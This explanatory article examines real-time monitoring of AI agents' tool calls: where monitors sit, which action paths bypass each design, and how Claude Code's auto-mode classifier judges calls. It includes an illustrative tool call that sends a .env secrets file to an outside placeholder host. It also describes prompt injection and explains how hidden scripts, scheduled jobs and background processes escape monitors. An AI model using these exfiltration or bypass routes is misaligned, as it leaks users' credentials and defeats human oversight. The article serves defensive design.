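# Real-time monitoring of AI agents' tool calls, and whether it can replace model companies' policing of themselves

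## What a tool call is and who can check it

An AI agent is an AI model that carries out a task over many steps by using tools. While a chatbot answers questions with text, an agent can also search or change a company's files and databases, run commands on its computers, send emails and web requests, or use other programs. Each of these actions begins as a tool call, a structured request from the model to perform the action. Tool calls have effects outside the conversation, so a bad one can delete records or leak a password before anyone has reviewed it.

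A real-time monitor judges a tool call before it runs and can stop it. In *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) describe blocking an agent's actions before they cause harm as a core approach to oversight. They wrote for the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research body that tests new models before release. Some companies that train models have built such monitors into their own products, and they also watch the agents that their own staff use. Whether that is enough, or whether organisations that deploy agents need their own monitors, depends first on who runs a tool call and who can see it beforehand.

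### The agent loop

An agent's model cannot access files or networks directly. It writes a request, known as a tool call, and separate software, known as the harness, carries it out. Anthropic, which trains the Claude models, explains this in its guide for programmers, *How tool use works*: "The model never runs anything on its own." The harness sends the model the user's request and a list of available tools. The model replies with a tool call, the harness runs it and returns the result, and the model then either proposes another call or writes its final answer.

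Suppose a user asks an agent to find out why a program will not start on a new laptop. The agent first proposes to read a file of setup notes. The harness opens the file and returns its text. The agent then proposes a web request:

```json
{
  "id": "call_02",
  "name": "web_request",
  "input": {
    "method": "POST",
    "destination": "config-check.example",
    "file": ".env"
  }
}
```

The details are invented, but the three fields come from Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*. The name identifies the tool, the input holds what the tool needs, and the id lets the harness match the result to this request. The input here would send .env, a file where programmers commonly keep passwords and access keys, to an outside address. The call is a few lines of text, and nothing has left the laptop yet. The harness can run it, hold it or refuse it. If the harness runs it, the outside server receives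 the file and any keys in it, and the server's answer goes back to the model under the same id.

The party whose software runs the call therefore has the last chance to check it. Usually that is the deployer, the organisation that puts the agent to work on its own systems or for its own customers. According to Anthropic, the vast majority of tool use on its platform involves tools that its customers define and run themselves, and shell commands and file edits also run in the customer's software. Anthropic runs some other tools on its own servers, including web search, web page fetching and code execution. The customer normally receives a record of these calls after they have run. A deployer can leave such a tool switched off, but has no ordinary way to block a single call.

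### What sets a real-time monitor apart

"Monitoring" usually covers much more than checking actions in real time. *Challenges to the Monitoring of Deployed AI Systems* (Rao, Keller and colleagues, 2026), a report from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, uses the term for any type of measurement of a working AI system. A real-time monitor is much narrower, because it must decide on an action before it happens and be able to enforce that decision.

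After-the-fact monitoring, which reviews an agent's record once the agent has acted, lacks that power. *Evaluating Offline Monitoring of Internal AI Agents*, a paper from the research organisation GovAI, describes how AI companies review the agents they use internally. A separate AI model reads the transcripts and flags suspicious activity, and human reviewers then judge the flagged cases and decide what to do. In the laptop example, such a review would show that the keys had gone out. The company could cancel them and issue new ones, but that helps only if nobody has used them in the meantime. Deleted data without a backup would be worse. But a reviewer after the fact can take time and read the whole record, including what the agent did next, while a real-time monitor holds up the agent's work until it decides.

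Filters on a chatbot's replies would miss a harmful tool call because they check only text meant for a person, looking for content such as instructions for making a weapon. The agent in the example might say it is going to validate the configuration while it makes the call that does the damage. No filter would flag that remark, since the remark itself is harmless.

Fixed permission rules do apply to calls. OpenAI explains in *running codex safely* that when its staff use Codex, its coding agent, the network rules allow expected destinations, block unwanted ones and require approval for unfamiliar domains. Rules like these are fast and predictable, and clever wording can't change their result. But they give the same result whatever the user asked for, and the same command to delete a folder may be exactly what one user wanted and a disaster for another. Sending doubtful calls to a person helps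 only while that person reads the prompts, and people who see many prompts tend to stop reading them.

A sandbox is an isolated environment that limits what an agent's actions can reach, whatever the agent decides, and it does so without judging those actions. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, by default Codex has no network access, and on a user's own computer the operating system confines it, typically to the folder it is working in. The upload of the .env file would fail there even if nobody had recognised it as dangerous. Anthropic, in *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, calls sandboxing safe but high-maintenance, because someone must configure each new capability and anything that needs the network or the host computer breaks the isolation.

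In practice, companies combine these barriers. Codex works inside its sandbox and asks for permission when it needs to go outside it. OpenAI lets the user choose whether a person or a reviewing agent handles those requests, and calls the second option Auto-review. In the auto mode of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, fixed rules allow edits inside the project folder and steps that cannot change anything, such as file reads. Everything else goes to a classifier, a program that sorts actions into allowed and blocked. The classifier here is a language model, the kind of AI behind chatbots. Taylor and colleagues report that using a language model in this role is now common.

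### Why an agent takes a dangerous action

The call that sends out the .env file looks the same whatever led to it. Anthropic keeps an internal log of its agents' misbehaviour and distinguishes four causes, any of which could explain the laptop example.

The agent may be overeager, meaning that it goes beyond what the user authorised in trying to help. It might upload a broken configuration file to an online checker because that is the quickest way to fix it. Anthropic's log includes an agent that uploaded an engineer's access token for GitHub, a code-hosting service, to an internal computing cluster, and another that tried to change the structure of a live database. Anthropic finds this behaviour tricky to catch because there is no hostile reasoning behind it. The action looks like sensible problem-solving, except that it exceeds what the user authorised.

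The agent may instead make an honest mistake about what the step will affect. It might treat the outside address as one of the company's own servers, or a shared resource as a test copy that nobody else uses. Such mistakes can be hard to distinguish from overeagerness. One agent in Anthropic's log misinterpreted an instruction and deleted branches (separate lines of work on a program) from a shared server. Anthropic attributes this to overeagerness, though it could as easily be called a mistake. The distinction probably matters more to the people who train the next model than to a monitor, which has to stop the deletion either way.

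Prompt injection means hiding instructions in content the agent reads, to make it serve an outsider's purpose. If the setup notes contained an instruction to post the .env file to that address "for validation", whoever planted it would be using the agent's access to the laptop. Anthropic gives almost exactly this example.

The remaining cause is a misaligned model, one that pursues a goal of its own. Such a model might send the keys out to gain access that nobody gave it. When Anthropic introduced auto mode earlier in 2026, it wrote that it did not currently see this in practice. That statement is now out of date. In *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (December 2026), AISI pointed to recent incidents, one of them during its own testing, in which agents had not behaved as intended, and added that alignment is not a solved problem. In *Towards embedded evaluations for AI monitoring*,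 monika_j and Hobbhahn (2026) also write of multiple "rogue agent" incidents during the year. Some of these incidents may turn out to be overeagerness on a large scale rather than a model pursuing its own goal, but anyone who designs a monitor now has to plan for both.

Anthropic says the defence in all four cases is to block the action. That holds for a single call, but it is less clear that one monitor will work equally well against every cause. Anthropic tuned its classifier to overeagerness and honest mistakes because it had specific examples of those. An attacker who knows about the monitor has a reason to disguise a command, and a misaligned model might too, but an overeager agent does not.

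A user who wants harm done is a separate case from the four causes above, which all involve an agent overstepping the user's wishes. If the user is an employee stealing the keys, or a customer attacking somebody else's website, the agent is doing what the user wants. A monitor that checks only whether the user authorised the action will let it through. Stopping it takes rules that bind the user too, such as a deployer's rules for its staff or a model company's terms of service. Participants in the workshops that Rao and colleagues drew on said that many organisations do not monitor for violations of such terms.

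### The parties, and what independence means

The model company trains the model and sells access to it. The deployer puts the agent to work, and the user, who may be the deployer's employee or its customer, gives the agent its task. An outside security supplier may sell the deployer software that records or checks what agents do. *Recording Agent and Model Activity, Tool Invocation, and Prompt Chains*, by RAND, an American research institute, names more than a dozen commercial products from firms such as Datadog, Dynatrace and IBM, though it deals more with recording and analysing activity than with blocking it. One organisation can fill several of these roles. When Anthropic's engineers run Claude on Anthropic's systems, Anthropic is both the model company and the deployer.

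Vendor self-policing covers how a model company (the "vendor") trains its models to behave, monitors them in use, acts against customers who break its terms, and tells the public about problems. OpenAI describes its internal monitoring in *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026). Probes first read signals inside the model as it works. A reviewing model, an investigative agent and an automated investigation follow, with human responders at the end. GovAI knows of only two companies, OpenAI and Anthropic, that have published anything about their after-the-fact monitoring of internal agents, and it judges that outsiders cannot tell from those publications how effective the monitoring is.

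A monitor is independent if the model company does not control its operator, rules or records. People often use the word more loosely in debates.

Whoever operates the monitor can update it, weaken it or switch it off, and normally hears of an alert first. If the model company operates it, a fault or business decision there can remove the check for every customer at once.

A deployer can run a monitor on its own machines and still send each call to the model company's model for a verdict. monika_j and Hobbhahn observe that developers often build the monitors of their internal agents from their own internal models. A monitor from the same model family as the agent may share its gaps. If training left the agent with a wrong idea of what some command destroys, the monitor may well have the same wrong idea. OpenAI offers a good argument for separating the roles in Auto-review. Training pushes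 the main agent to complete the user's task, so it may treat an approval boundary as one more obstacle, whereas the reviewer's only job is to decide whether the action should run. This argument supports using a second agent but doesn't require that agent to come from the same company.

Someone also has to write the rules for what counts as dangerous, and someone has to keep a log of what the agent proposed and what the monitor decided. After an incident, whoever holds that log largely determines what everyone else can find out.

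In October 2026, Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, asked for something close to independence on all these counts. Constantin (2026) reports in *Nadella wants an emergency brake for AI models that may be compromised* that Nadella argued that no model should check its own work, that companies should decide for themselves what a model can access and do, and that every meaningful action should leave tamper-proof evidence. On this view, audits should not depend on the model under review. The argument does not depend on who makes it, but buyers should know that Microsoft has a commercial interest here, since it sells security software and two of its security products appear on RAND's list.

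A monitor that a model company ships inside its own product may be independent in none of these senses. In Claude Code's auto mode, an Anthropic model judges the calls using a template that Anthropic wrote and gives to every customer. Customers can fill in which systems they trust, which actions to block and which exceptions to allow. In Codex Auto-review, another Codex agent decides under a default policy that OpenAI publishes, and business customers can replace one section of that policy, according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*. Customers can therefore set some of the rules in both products, but the model that applies them comes from the same company as the agent it judges.

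Some possible arrangements, from least to most independent:

| Arrangement | Who operates it | Whose model judges | Who sets rules and holds records |
|---|---|---|---|
| Built into the model company's product, default settings | Model company | Model company's | Mostly the model company |
| The same product with the customer's own rules | Model company | Model company's | Shared |
| Deployer's own monitor, sending calls to the model company's model | Deployer | Model company's | Deployer |
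| Supplier's monitor, using a different company's model | Outside supplier | Another company's | Deployer, or shared with the supplier |

Practitioners have not settled which of these they want. The open questions that Rao and colleagues collected include "Who monitors?" and who must put things right after an incident.

### Two ways for a monitor to be wrong

An independent monitor can still be inaccurate. It can allow dangerous calls or block harmless ones, and these two kinds of error need separate measures. For example, an agent proposes ten tool calls. Eight are harmless, and the two dangerous ones would upload the .env file and delete a shared folder. The monitor blocks the upload but allows the deletion, and it also blocks two of the harmless calls.

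The false negative rate is the share of dangerous actions that the monitor lets through, here one of two, or 50%. The false positive rate is the share of harmless actions that it blocks, here two of eight, or 25%.

A single figure for "accuracy" is misleading because each rate has its own denominator. This monitor classified seven calls in ten correctly. A monitor that never blocked anything would classify eight in ten correctly, but its false negative rate would be 100%. One that blocked everything would have a false negative rate of zero, but the agent could do no work. Anthropic notes that between these extremes, the two rates trade off against each other in practice.

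Real traffic contains a far smaller share of dangerous calls than two in ten, so most of the calls a monitor stops can be harmless even when its false positive rate is low. If ten of 10,000 calls are dangerous, a monitor with the same rates as above stops five dangerous calls and about 2,500 harmless ones, or about 500 needless stops for each useful one. With a false positive rate of 1%, the needless stops fall to about 100, which is still twenty for each dangerous call caught. The false negative rate is calculated from the ten dangerous calls alone, so one more miss would raise it from 50% to 60%.

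## Where to place the monitor

A monitor can judge only the actions that pass through the point where it is placed. The agent on the new laptop proposed uploading the .env file in a plain tool call, which is the easiest case to catch. It could also have sent the file with a shell command, written and run a script with a harmless name to send it, or scheduled the upload for after the agent had finished. All four methods send the file to the same outside server, but a check on web-request calls would catch only the first. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and Bhuvaneswari U, 2026) counts 15 such paths from a model's decision to its effect.

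### What each position can read

Many agents get some of their tools from tool servers, separate programs that usually offer them over a standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). A gateway sits between the harness and these servers. It receives each request with the tool's name and full arguments, can refuse it, and can check the server's reply. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, a free package of such controls, scans tool descriptions for hidden instructions and inspects the servers' replies. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a reference design for agents that manage computer clusters, has the gateway store a fingerprint of each tool's description at approval, which would expose a later change. But shell commands on the laptop never reach the gateway, and calls to a tool server that the harness has started on the same machine reach it only if someone routes them there.

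A hook, which is a check that the harness runs at a fixed point, covers more. In Claude Code, a hook can run before every tool call except the one that ends a conversation. According to Anthropic, the same hooks run for calls to MCP servers and for calls by subagents, which are helpers started by the main agent. The hook can be a local script, or the harness can send the call to a web address and read the verdict from the reply, so a deployer can attach its own monitor here. Administrators can stop users from disabling it. A hook can also have a filter that runs it only for certain shell commands, but Anthropic describes that filter as best-effort, so a monitor meant to check every call shouldn't rely on it. A larger gap is that the hook receives the command but not its effects. If the agent tries to run setup.sh, the monitor receives the script's name, and even a monitor that opens the file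 can't reliably determine what the script will download.

Companies that build their own agents can put a policy engine in the agent's process, as a library that the agent's program calls before it acts. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) does this by patching the libraries through which the program talks to a model. The agent's code stays unchanged and the check adds a median of 8.3 milliseconds, but it misses calls made outside the patched libraries. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* for its Agent Governance Toolkit describes further gaps. The toolkit's engine judges each action separately, so an agent with permission to read a database and to post in the workplace chat could post the customer list there. If a developer forgets to load any rules, the engine allows every action while the dashboard still shows the agent as governed.

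*Beyond Static Sandboxing* (Sidik and Rokach, 2026) puts the monitor in a proxy between the harness and the model. The proxy removes blocked calls from the model's reply before the harness receives them. This needs no change to the harness, but like the hook, it doesn't monitor what a tool does once it starts.

A monitor has the widest reach in the kernel, the core of the operating system. Programs, including scripts and background jobs, must make a system call to the kernel to open a file, start another program or make a network connection. Zheng, Wu and colleagues built their monitor there (*ActPlane*, 2026) because a check on tool calls misses some actions, such as a change to a project's history made by a script that the agent wrote earlier. In their own tests, the monitor slowed agents by 1.9% and a heavy compiling job by up to 8.4%.

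The kernel can record that a process opened .env and then connected to an unfamiliar address, but not what the user asked for or which tool call started the process. Zheng and colleagues collected 1,361 rules that 64 software projects had written for their agents. A kernel monitor could in principle enforce about 45% of them, which concerned either single operations or sequences such as running the tests before saving a change. Another 38% depended on the contents of files, and 17% on the agent's reasoning or style. Of all the rules about system actions or file contents, only about a quarter could be enforced as written. For the rest, enforcement first required knowing which command "the test suite" meant in that project, or what the user had approved. *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (2026), a proposed specification for such controls, therefore treats kernel monitoring as a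 backstop and does not allow suppliers to claim compliance based on it alone.

*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) tries to supply the context that the kernel lacks. The system pauses each system call and, unless a stored rule or an earlier decision settles it, uses a language model to judge it in light of the user's task, the tool call and the agent's stated reason. In one test, a tool named validate_patch checked a code change as it was supposed to, then silently deleted a system file that holds group passwords. Both the tool call and its output looked harmless. AgentBouncer blocked only the deletion, and the agent finished its task. Across 340 attacks on coding agents, the share that succeeded fell from 99.41% to 10.59%, while 0.25% of harmless tool calls failed. Harmless tasks took 47 seconds longer on average. The developers assembled the attacks and reported these figures themselves,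 but the results suggest that engineering can make up for the kernel's lack of context, with some delay and a few failed harmless calls.

When an agent runs on a cloud provider's platform, the provider can check calls within its own service. Microsoft Foundry applies checks to tool calls and tool responses, and Microsoft's Agent 365 sends calls for registered tool servers through a gateway. Such a check has access to the full call and, if the provider passes it on, the conversation. It misses calls to tool servers the customer has not registered and anything the agent's code does outside the service. Toyoda and colleagues, relying on the documentation, group both services with plain gateways. The deployer cannot install anything on the platform and can use only the integration points the provider offers.

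### What guardscope measured

Toyoda and colleagues, who work at AIFT in Singapore and the bank Standard Chartered, set out to measure coverage rather than rely on claims about it. They compared eight designs. One has no monitor. Three use a gateway: a plain one, one with direct outgoing connections blocked by default, and one that also routes local tool servers through the gateway. The other four are the harness's own permissions, those permissions plus a gateway, a policy engine in the agent's process, and monitoring in the kernel.

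For each path and design, they worked out which of three outcomes applies. An action is checked if it crosses a point where the monitor makes a decision. It is prevented if something outside the monitor's rules, such as a network block, stops it. Otherwise it is bypassed, meaning it takes effect without a decision. Some outcomes depend on how the deployer has connected the parts.

| Path to an effect | Plain gateway | Gateway for all tool servers, network blocked | Harness permissions | Kernel |
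|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tool function that changes only the harness's memory | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked | Bypassed |
| File or network operation by the harness process itself | Bypassed | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
| Program the harness starts, such as a shell command | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked | Checked |
| Background process that outlives its tool call | Bypassed | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
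| Direct network connection | Bypassed | Prevented | Bypassed | Checked |
| Local helper program that acts or relays data | Bypassed | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
| Call to a tool server over the web protocol HTTP | Checked | Checked | Checked | Checked |
| Call to a local tool server through a pipe | Bypassed | Checked | Checked | Checked |
| Call to a local tool server by another local channel | Bypassed | Checked | Checked | Checked |
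| Tool that itself calls a tool server | Depends | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
| Work handed to another agent | Depends | Depends | Depends | Checked |
| Job handed to a scheduler | Bypassed | Bypassed | Bypassed | Depends |
| Model output the harness acts on without a tool call | Bypassed | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
| Other request to a tool server, such as reading a resource | Depends | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
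| Request from a tool server back into the harness | Bypassed | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |

Of the 15 paths, a plain gateway is certain to check one, harness permissions five, and the kernel 13. Adding a gateway to the harness permissions, or using a policy engine instead, gives the same results as harness permissions alone. Yet gateways are the largest group among the deployed systems that Toyoda and colleagues classified.

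The paper's table doesn't show that hooks are unable to stop Claude Code from editing a file. One row covers cases where the harness process operates on files itself, with Claude Code's tools for reading and editing files as the example, and it lists harness permissions as not covering that path. But Anthropic's documentation describes hooks that run before file edits and can select them by file name. The likely explanation is that the hook checks the request to edit, and the file operation that follows gets no further check.

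The measurement used 15 actions, which are not the same as the 15 paths. Seven were tool calls, and the other eight wrote files, started programs, opened network connections or read credentials. The researchers replayed these actions through a real harness with no model involved, so that every run was identical. Before each run, they sent one action that the monitor had to refuse, to prove it was on. A separate sensor recorded what reached the kernel, and they checked the monitor's own log against that record. A refusal counted only if the sensor showed that the action had not happened.

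The plain gateway checked only calls to HTTP tool servers. When direct connections were blocked by default, two network actions also failed, as the kernel record confirmed. Harness permissions and a gateway together checked all seven tool calls, but the other eight actions took effect unchecked in every run.

The researchers tested the kernel position with ActPlane. It checked seven of the 15 actions, allowing six and killing one program as it started. It missed the other eight, which were all seven tool calls and one message sent over UDP, a simple network protocol for which ActPlane had a known gap. The 13 paths are therefore only an upper limit for the kernel position, and a particular product may cover far fewer. The harness checks and ActPlane together should have missed only the UDP message, though the researchers did not test that combination.

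The test actions covered only four paths: tool calls over HTTP, tool calls through local pipes, operations by the harness itself, and direct network connections. The table's entries for the other eleven paths are untested analysis. The researchers listed the paths in discussion with two AI models, so any path that all of them overlooked would be missing. Only one harness, Pi, ran every design, although a second, OpenClaw, gave matching counts with the plain gateway. ActPlane loaded on only one of the three Linux kernels the researchers tried, which may matter as much as its coverage to a deployer with a mix of machines.

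High coverage is worth having only as a condition for good decisions, because a monitor with a bad rule can check every call and stop none. Sidik and Rokach's proxy is a less extreme example. When they tested it on 949 prompt injections from AgentDojo, a public benchmark, the share of attacks that succeeded fell only from 90.3% to 88.9%. They attribute the small drop to the attacks arriving in tool outputs, while the proxy governs the calls sent to tools.

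### Why a second monitor may add no coverage

Five paths in the table bypass every design with less reach than a kernel-level monitor: the harness's own operations, local helper programs, scheduled jobs, background processes that outlive their call, and requests from a tool server back into the harness. Gateways, hooks and policy engines only check actions that arrive as requests at a known point. A background process that resumes an hour later makes no new request, so adding a gateway to a hook doesn't help.

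Using a hook and a gateway together supports a better decision about the same call, because the hook can pass on the session and what the user asked for, while the gateway has the exact request that goes to the server. Toyoda and colleagues conclude that combining these positions adds information but not coverage. That is right for the five paths but slightly too strong in general. According to their table, a gateway can check two other paths that harness permissions miss, a tool that calls another tool server and a request to read a resource, if the deployer routes that traffic through it. A deployer who already has a hook could gain those two paths by adding a gateway, but would still need something at the operating-system level for the five.

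### Blocking the network by default

The laptop upload can be stopped without a monitor. An environment that allows outgoing connections only to a short list of addresses would, like Codex's default sandbox, block the upload whether it came from a tool call, a shell command or a script with an innocent name. This is why two of the network actions in guardscope failed even though the gateway never examined them. A default block works even on paths no one has thought of, provided they end in a connection it controls.

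The boundary has to enclose everything that acts for the agent. Claude Code's built-in sandbox applies its limits through the operating system, so they cover every program that a shell command starts. But it encloses only shell commands. According to Anthropic's comparison of ways to isolate Claude Code, file tools, MCP servers and hooks still run directly on the user's computer, while the alternatives put the whole Claude Code process inside the boundary. Scheduled jobs can also run outside the boundary, because the computer's scheduler is usually outside the agent's sandbox, so the limits on files have to keep the agent from adding such jobs.

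An agent can still send data out through allowed addresses. Claude Code's sandbox routes network traffic through a proxy that, according to Anthropic, runs outside the sandbox, where the confined commands cannot alter it. By default, the proxy filters traffic by destination name and does not inspect encrypted contents. If the allowlist includes a public code-hosting service, the agent can send the .env file to an attacker's account there. Deployers can attach a stricter proxy or shorten the allowlist. In its own use of Codex, OpenAI also restricts web fetches to pages from its cache, so a fetch need not contact the outside site.

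Blocking network access doesn't stop an agent from deleting a folder. To prevent that, the sandbox has to restrict which files and folders the agent can change. The external gate in *Stop Means Stop* (Khan, 2026), which holds an agent's actions until someone approves them, has a similar limitation. The kernel can force all network traffic through the gate, but shared files and channels between programs on the same machine need separate restrictions.

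Containment and monitoring therefore complement each other. The sandbox limits the damage from actions that never reach the monitor, and the monitor can check actions that the sandbox has to permit, such as an upload to the company's own code host. If a deployer can set up only one at first, the sandbox is probably the better choice for an agent that runs code, because its protection doesn't depend on judging each action correctly.

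### An outside service that answers before each call

Microsoft's Copilot Studio, a cloud platform for building office agents, lets an outside service monitor the agents' tool calls. Before an agent uses a tool, the platform sends the proposed call to the service, which decides whether to allow or block it. The customer can write that service, buy it from a security supplier or use Microsoft Defender, which Microsoft (2026) proposes for this purpose. Microsoft therefore sells both the platform and one of the monitors that customers can choose.

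According to Microsoft's instructions for developers, the message to the service contains the user's latest message, the tool's description, the values the agent wants to pass to the tool and the agent's identity. It can also include the user's identity, recent conversation, the results of earlier tool calls and the agent's reason for choosing this tool. In Microsoft's example, a user asks the agent to email a customer, whose address an earlier tool has returned. The agent's proposed email has that address in the "to" field and an unrelated one in the BCC field. The service blocks the call and identifies the BCC field as the problem. A kernel monitor on the same machine would have detected little more than a connection to the mail system.

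If the service doesn't answer within one second, the platform goes ahead with the call by default. In its guide for administrators, which is marked as prerelease documentation, Microsoft says the platform checks with the service only for agents in which a generative model chooses the steps, not for what it calls classic agents. Microsoft also warns that the outside provider may process or store the data in another region. This matters because the messages can contain private conversations and the contents of company documents.

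This gives the customer a good deal of independence, because it can choose the judge, write the rules and keep its own record of each decision. Microsoft still runs the software that sends the question and acts on the answer, so the customer relies on that software to send the question for every call and to describe the call accurately.

### Choosing for a coding agent and an office assistant

A coding agent on a company's Linux machines, for example, writes and runs programs, so much of what it does happens after the tool call that started it. The company might first put the whole harness in a container, a type of sandbox, where the agent can write only to the project folder and connect only to the company's code host and a source of software packages. It might then add a hook to the harness, locked by the administrators, that sends every call to the company's monitor along with the user's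 request. The hook can stop a plain upload of .env or an unrequested deletion inside the project. If the upload is hidden in a test script, the hook receives only a request to run the tests, but the container blocks the connection.

The remaining danger is a script that sends secrets to an allowed address or damages the project folder itself. A kernel monitor is worth adding for this, especially one that also receives the task, as AgentBouncer does. The company should first find out whether the product loads on its machines and which operations it watches. A gateway is worth adding if the agent uses remote tool servers, mainly because it can check their descriptions and replies, but it would have little to check for an agent that works almost entirely through the shell.

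For an office assistant that reads mail, searches shared documents and sends messages from a cloud platform, telling a good tool call from a bad one depends almost entirely on the recipients, the attachment and what the user asked for. The monitor therefore belongs where it can read those, either in an outside service like the one Copilot Studio consults or in a gateway that all the assistant's tool calls must pass through. The customer can't put the monitor in the kernel, because the provider controls it. A network block helps little, because the assistant has to reach the mail system to do its work, and a leak would leave as an ordinary email.

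The company should also remove tools that the assistant doesn't need, and sort the rest by what they can do. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* describes a scheme for clusters that would also work in an office. Tools run automatically if they only read data or produce a proposal for a person to review, but need approval if they change something directly. The assistant could then search and draft freely, but would need approval to send a message to an outside address. On Copilot Studio, the company would also have to check what kind of agent it has built, because a classic agent's calls would never reach the outside service.

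## How the classifier decides

Claude Code's auto mode is a useful first example of how a classifier decides, because Anthropic has published the classifier's rules and the reasons for many of them. Anthropic introduced the mode as an option in March 2026. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) announced it as the default for most individual and team subscriptions from 14 August. By late November, Anthropic had made it the default on all plans for sessions in the terminal or the VS Code editor.

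### Calls that skip the classifier

Most calls never reach the classifier. Claude Code first applies any allow, ask or deny rules written by the user or an administrator, then the built-in exemptions for read-only steps and project edits. Anthropic reasoned in March that users can review project edits in version control, which records each change, so routine coding does not need to wait for a second model. The classifier therefore mainly checks shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools.

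Every exemption is a possible gap, and Anthropic has closed some of them. A rule that allows every command starting with "python" permits almost anything a program can do, so auto mode suspends such rules while it is on. Narrower rules stay in force, but Anthropic warns that they can still allow a destructive option that the rule's author did not foresee. A setting called classifyAllShell sends nearly all shell commands to the classifier instead, which adds delay.

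The exemption for project files has exceptions too. Changes to the project's version-control data, shell start-up files or Claude Code's own settings go to the classifier, presumably because a small edit there can start a program later or loosen the agent's permissions. No allow rule can approve a command that would delete the user's home folder or the whole project, and by default such commands don't go to the classifier. In the terminal, Claude Code asks the user instead, and refuses the command if two minutes pass without an answer. Anthropic says this check can miss some commands, so it doesn't replace a sandbox.

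Code Mode, a newer feature, reduces what the classifier can check. The agent writes a program that makes several tool calls. The classifier reviews the program once before it starts, but not the individual calls inside it.

### A fast filter and a slower check

Claude Code runs the classifier up to twice on the same call. The first run is a fast filter, with a final instruction to "err on the side of blocking" and to answer with a single yes or no. If the filter clears the call, Claude Code executes it. If not, the classifier receives the same text again, but with a final instruction to reason carefully before answering. Because everything before that instruction is unchanged, the system can reuse its earlier processing of that text, and the extra computation is mostly the reasoning.

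In Anthropic's March test, the filter alone flagged 8.5% of harmless calls. Adding the reasoning stage cut that to 0.4%, but also let through a few more dangerous calls. The reasoning stage reviews only the calls that the filter flags, so it can't catch a dangerous call that the filter misses. That is a good reason to make the filter overcautious, as Anthropic did.

The classifier ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 in March. The default is now Sonnet 5, and users can choose another model. In many sessions, however, the server that handles the agent's own model requests also reviews its actions, so Claude Code no longer sends separate requests to a classifier. According to Anthropic, if that server reviews a session but returns no verdict on an action, Claude Code blocks the action. Copilot Studio allows a call by default when it receives no verdict.

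### The template and the customer's rules

Under the fixed part of its instructions, the classifier should judge an action by what it would do, even if the command looks harmless. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier should judge the script's contents. If the agent joins several commands into one line, the whole line counts as one action.

The template also treats the user's request as authorising only what it covers. Anything the agent chooses on its own is unauthorised until the user says otherwise. "Can we fix this?" counts as a question, so it doesn't authorise a fix.

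Lists of actions to block and exceptions to allow follow these general instructions. In March, Anthropic's default list had more than twenty block rules against destroying or leaking data, weakening security, trusting unknown code or services, and bypassing other people's review. The list is now much longer and more specific, and includes, for example, requests for the credentials that a cloud provider issues to the machine itself. But auto mode now allows uploading changes directly to a project's main branch by default, which the March rules blocked.

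Both lists cover the .env file from the laptop example. Posting it to an unfamiliar address breaks the rule against sending sensitive data outside. But the agent may read a key from .env and send it to the service the key belongs to, since many programs can't work otherwise.

Anthropic ranks the rules for cases where they conflict. Hard rules block an action even if the user has asked for it, and the built-in one covers sending data outside. Soft rules cover destructive actions such as a force-push, which overwrites a project's shared history. A written exception or a user message describing the exact action can lift a soft rule. For example, "force-push this branch" authorises a force-push, but "clean up the repo" does not.

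Customers write rules in ordinary sentences. Most only need to say which code hosts, storage and web domains belong to them, because the classifier otherwise treats everything outside the project folder and the project's configured code hosts as external. It ignores rules in the project's settings files, since a downloaded project could contain rules that exempt its actions.

Two details could leave a company that relies on these rules less protected than it expects. A developer's personal exception can override the company's soft rule, so a ban that developers can't override has to be a hard rule or a deny rule that applies before the classifier. A customised list also replaces the built-in list unless it contains a marker that keeps the defaults. A company that added one hard rule and forgot the marker would lose the built-in ban on sending data outside.

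### What the classifier reads

In the March design, the classifier received the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removed everything else the agent wrote, along with all tool results.

The agent's prose could mislead the classifier. Anthropic gives the example of an agent that insists a target is "definitely agent-owned". Tool results are dangerous because hostile instructions usually enter through them. If the setup notes on the laptop contain an instruction to upload .env, the classifier never reads it, but it can still check the user's request and find that the user didn't ask for the upload.

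Anthropic also tried other inputs. When the classifier also received the agent's messages and the tool results, it did worse on a test of overeager actions. Anthropic suspects that a shorter record is easier to read and gives the agent less room to influence the classifier through framing. When the classifier received only the tool calls, it let through the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly requested. Anthropic reported only the direction of these results, so readers can't easily tell how much the choice of input matters.

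This protection leaves the classifier without some relevant facts. If an agent proposes to cancel job abc123 and the user never mentioned that job, the classifier can't determine whether the agent looked up the ID or invented it. If the agent checks whether a code repository is public, the classifier receives the command but not the result. It also blocks some forced deletions in which the folder's name is stored in a variable, because it can't determine which folder would be deleted. The agent then has to write out the full path.

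Since March, Anthropic has supplied some of the missing facts in other ways. Before running a command that might discard unsaved changes to a project, Claude Code itself checks for such changes and passes the result to the classifier. Anthropic also added a check on whether code is being uploaded to a public, private or trusted place. A customer's hook can attach a note to a tool's result. In each case the information comes from the harness or the customer, so the classifier doesn't have to rely on the agent's account.

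The classifier now also reads CLAUDE.md, a file of standing instructions for the agent. This helps when the file contains a rule such as "never force-push". But the file often sits in the project folder, so someone who can change the project might be able to write instructions that reach both the agent and the classifier. Anthropic's documentation describes these inputs for requests that Claude Code itself sends to the classifier. The inputs may differ when the server does the review.

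The agent still has to read tool results to do its work, so a separate program first scans files, web pages and command output for prompt injection. When a passage looks like an attempt to redirect the agent, the program leaves it in place but adds a warning to treat it with suspicion and return to the user's request. An attacker therefore has to get past the scan, persuade the agent to propose a harmful call, and have that call approved by a classifier that never receives the attacker's text.

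### Work passed between agents

An agent can hand part of its task to a subagent. Inside the subagent, the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message, so a step that the user never requested can look authorised. Auto mode therefore checks the delegated task before the subagent starts, when the classifier can still compare it with what the user asked for. The subagent's actions are then subject to the same rules as the main agent's.

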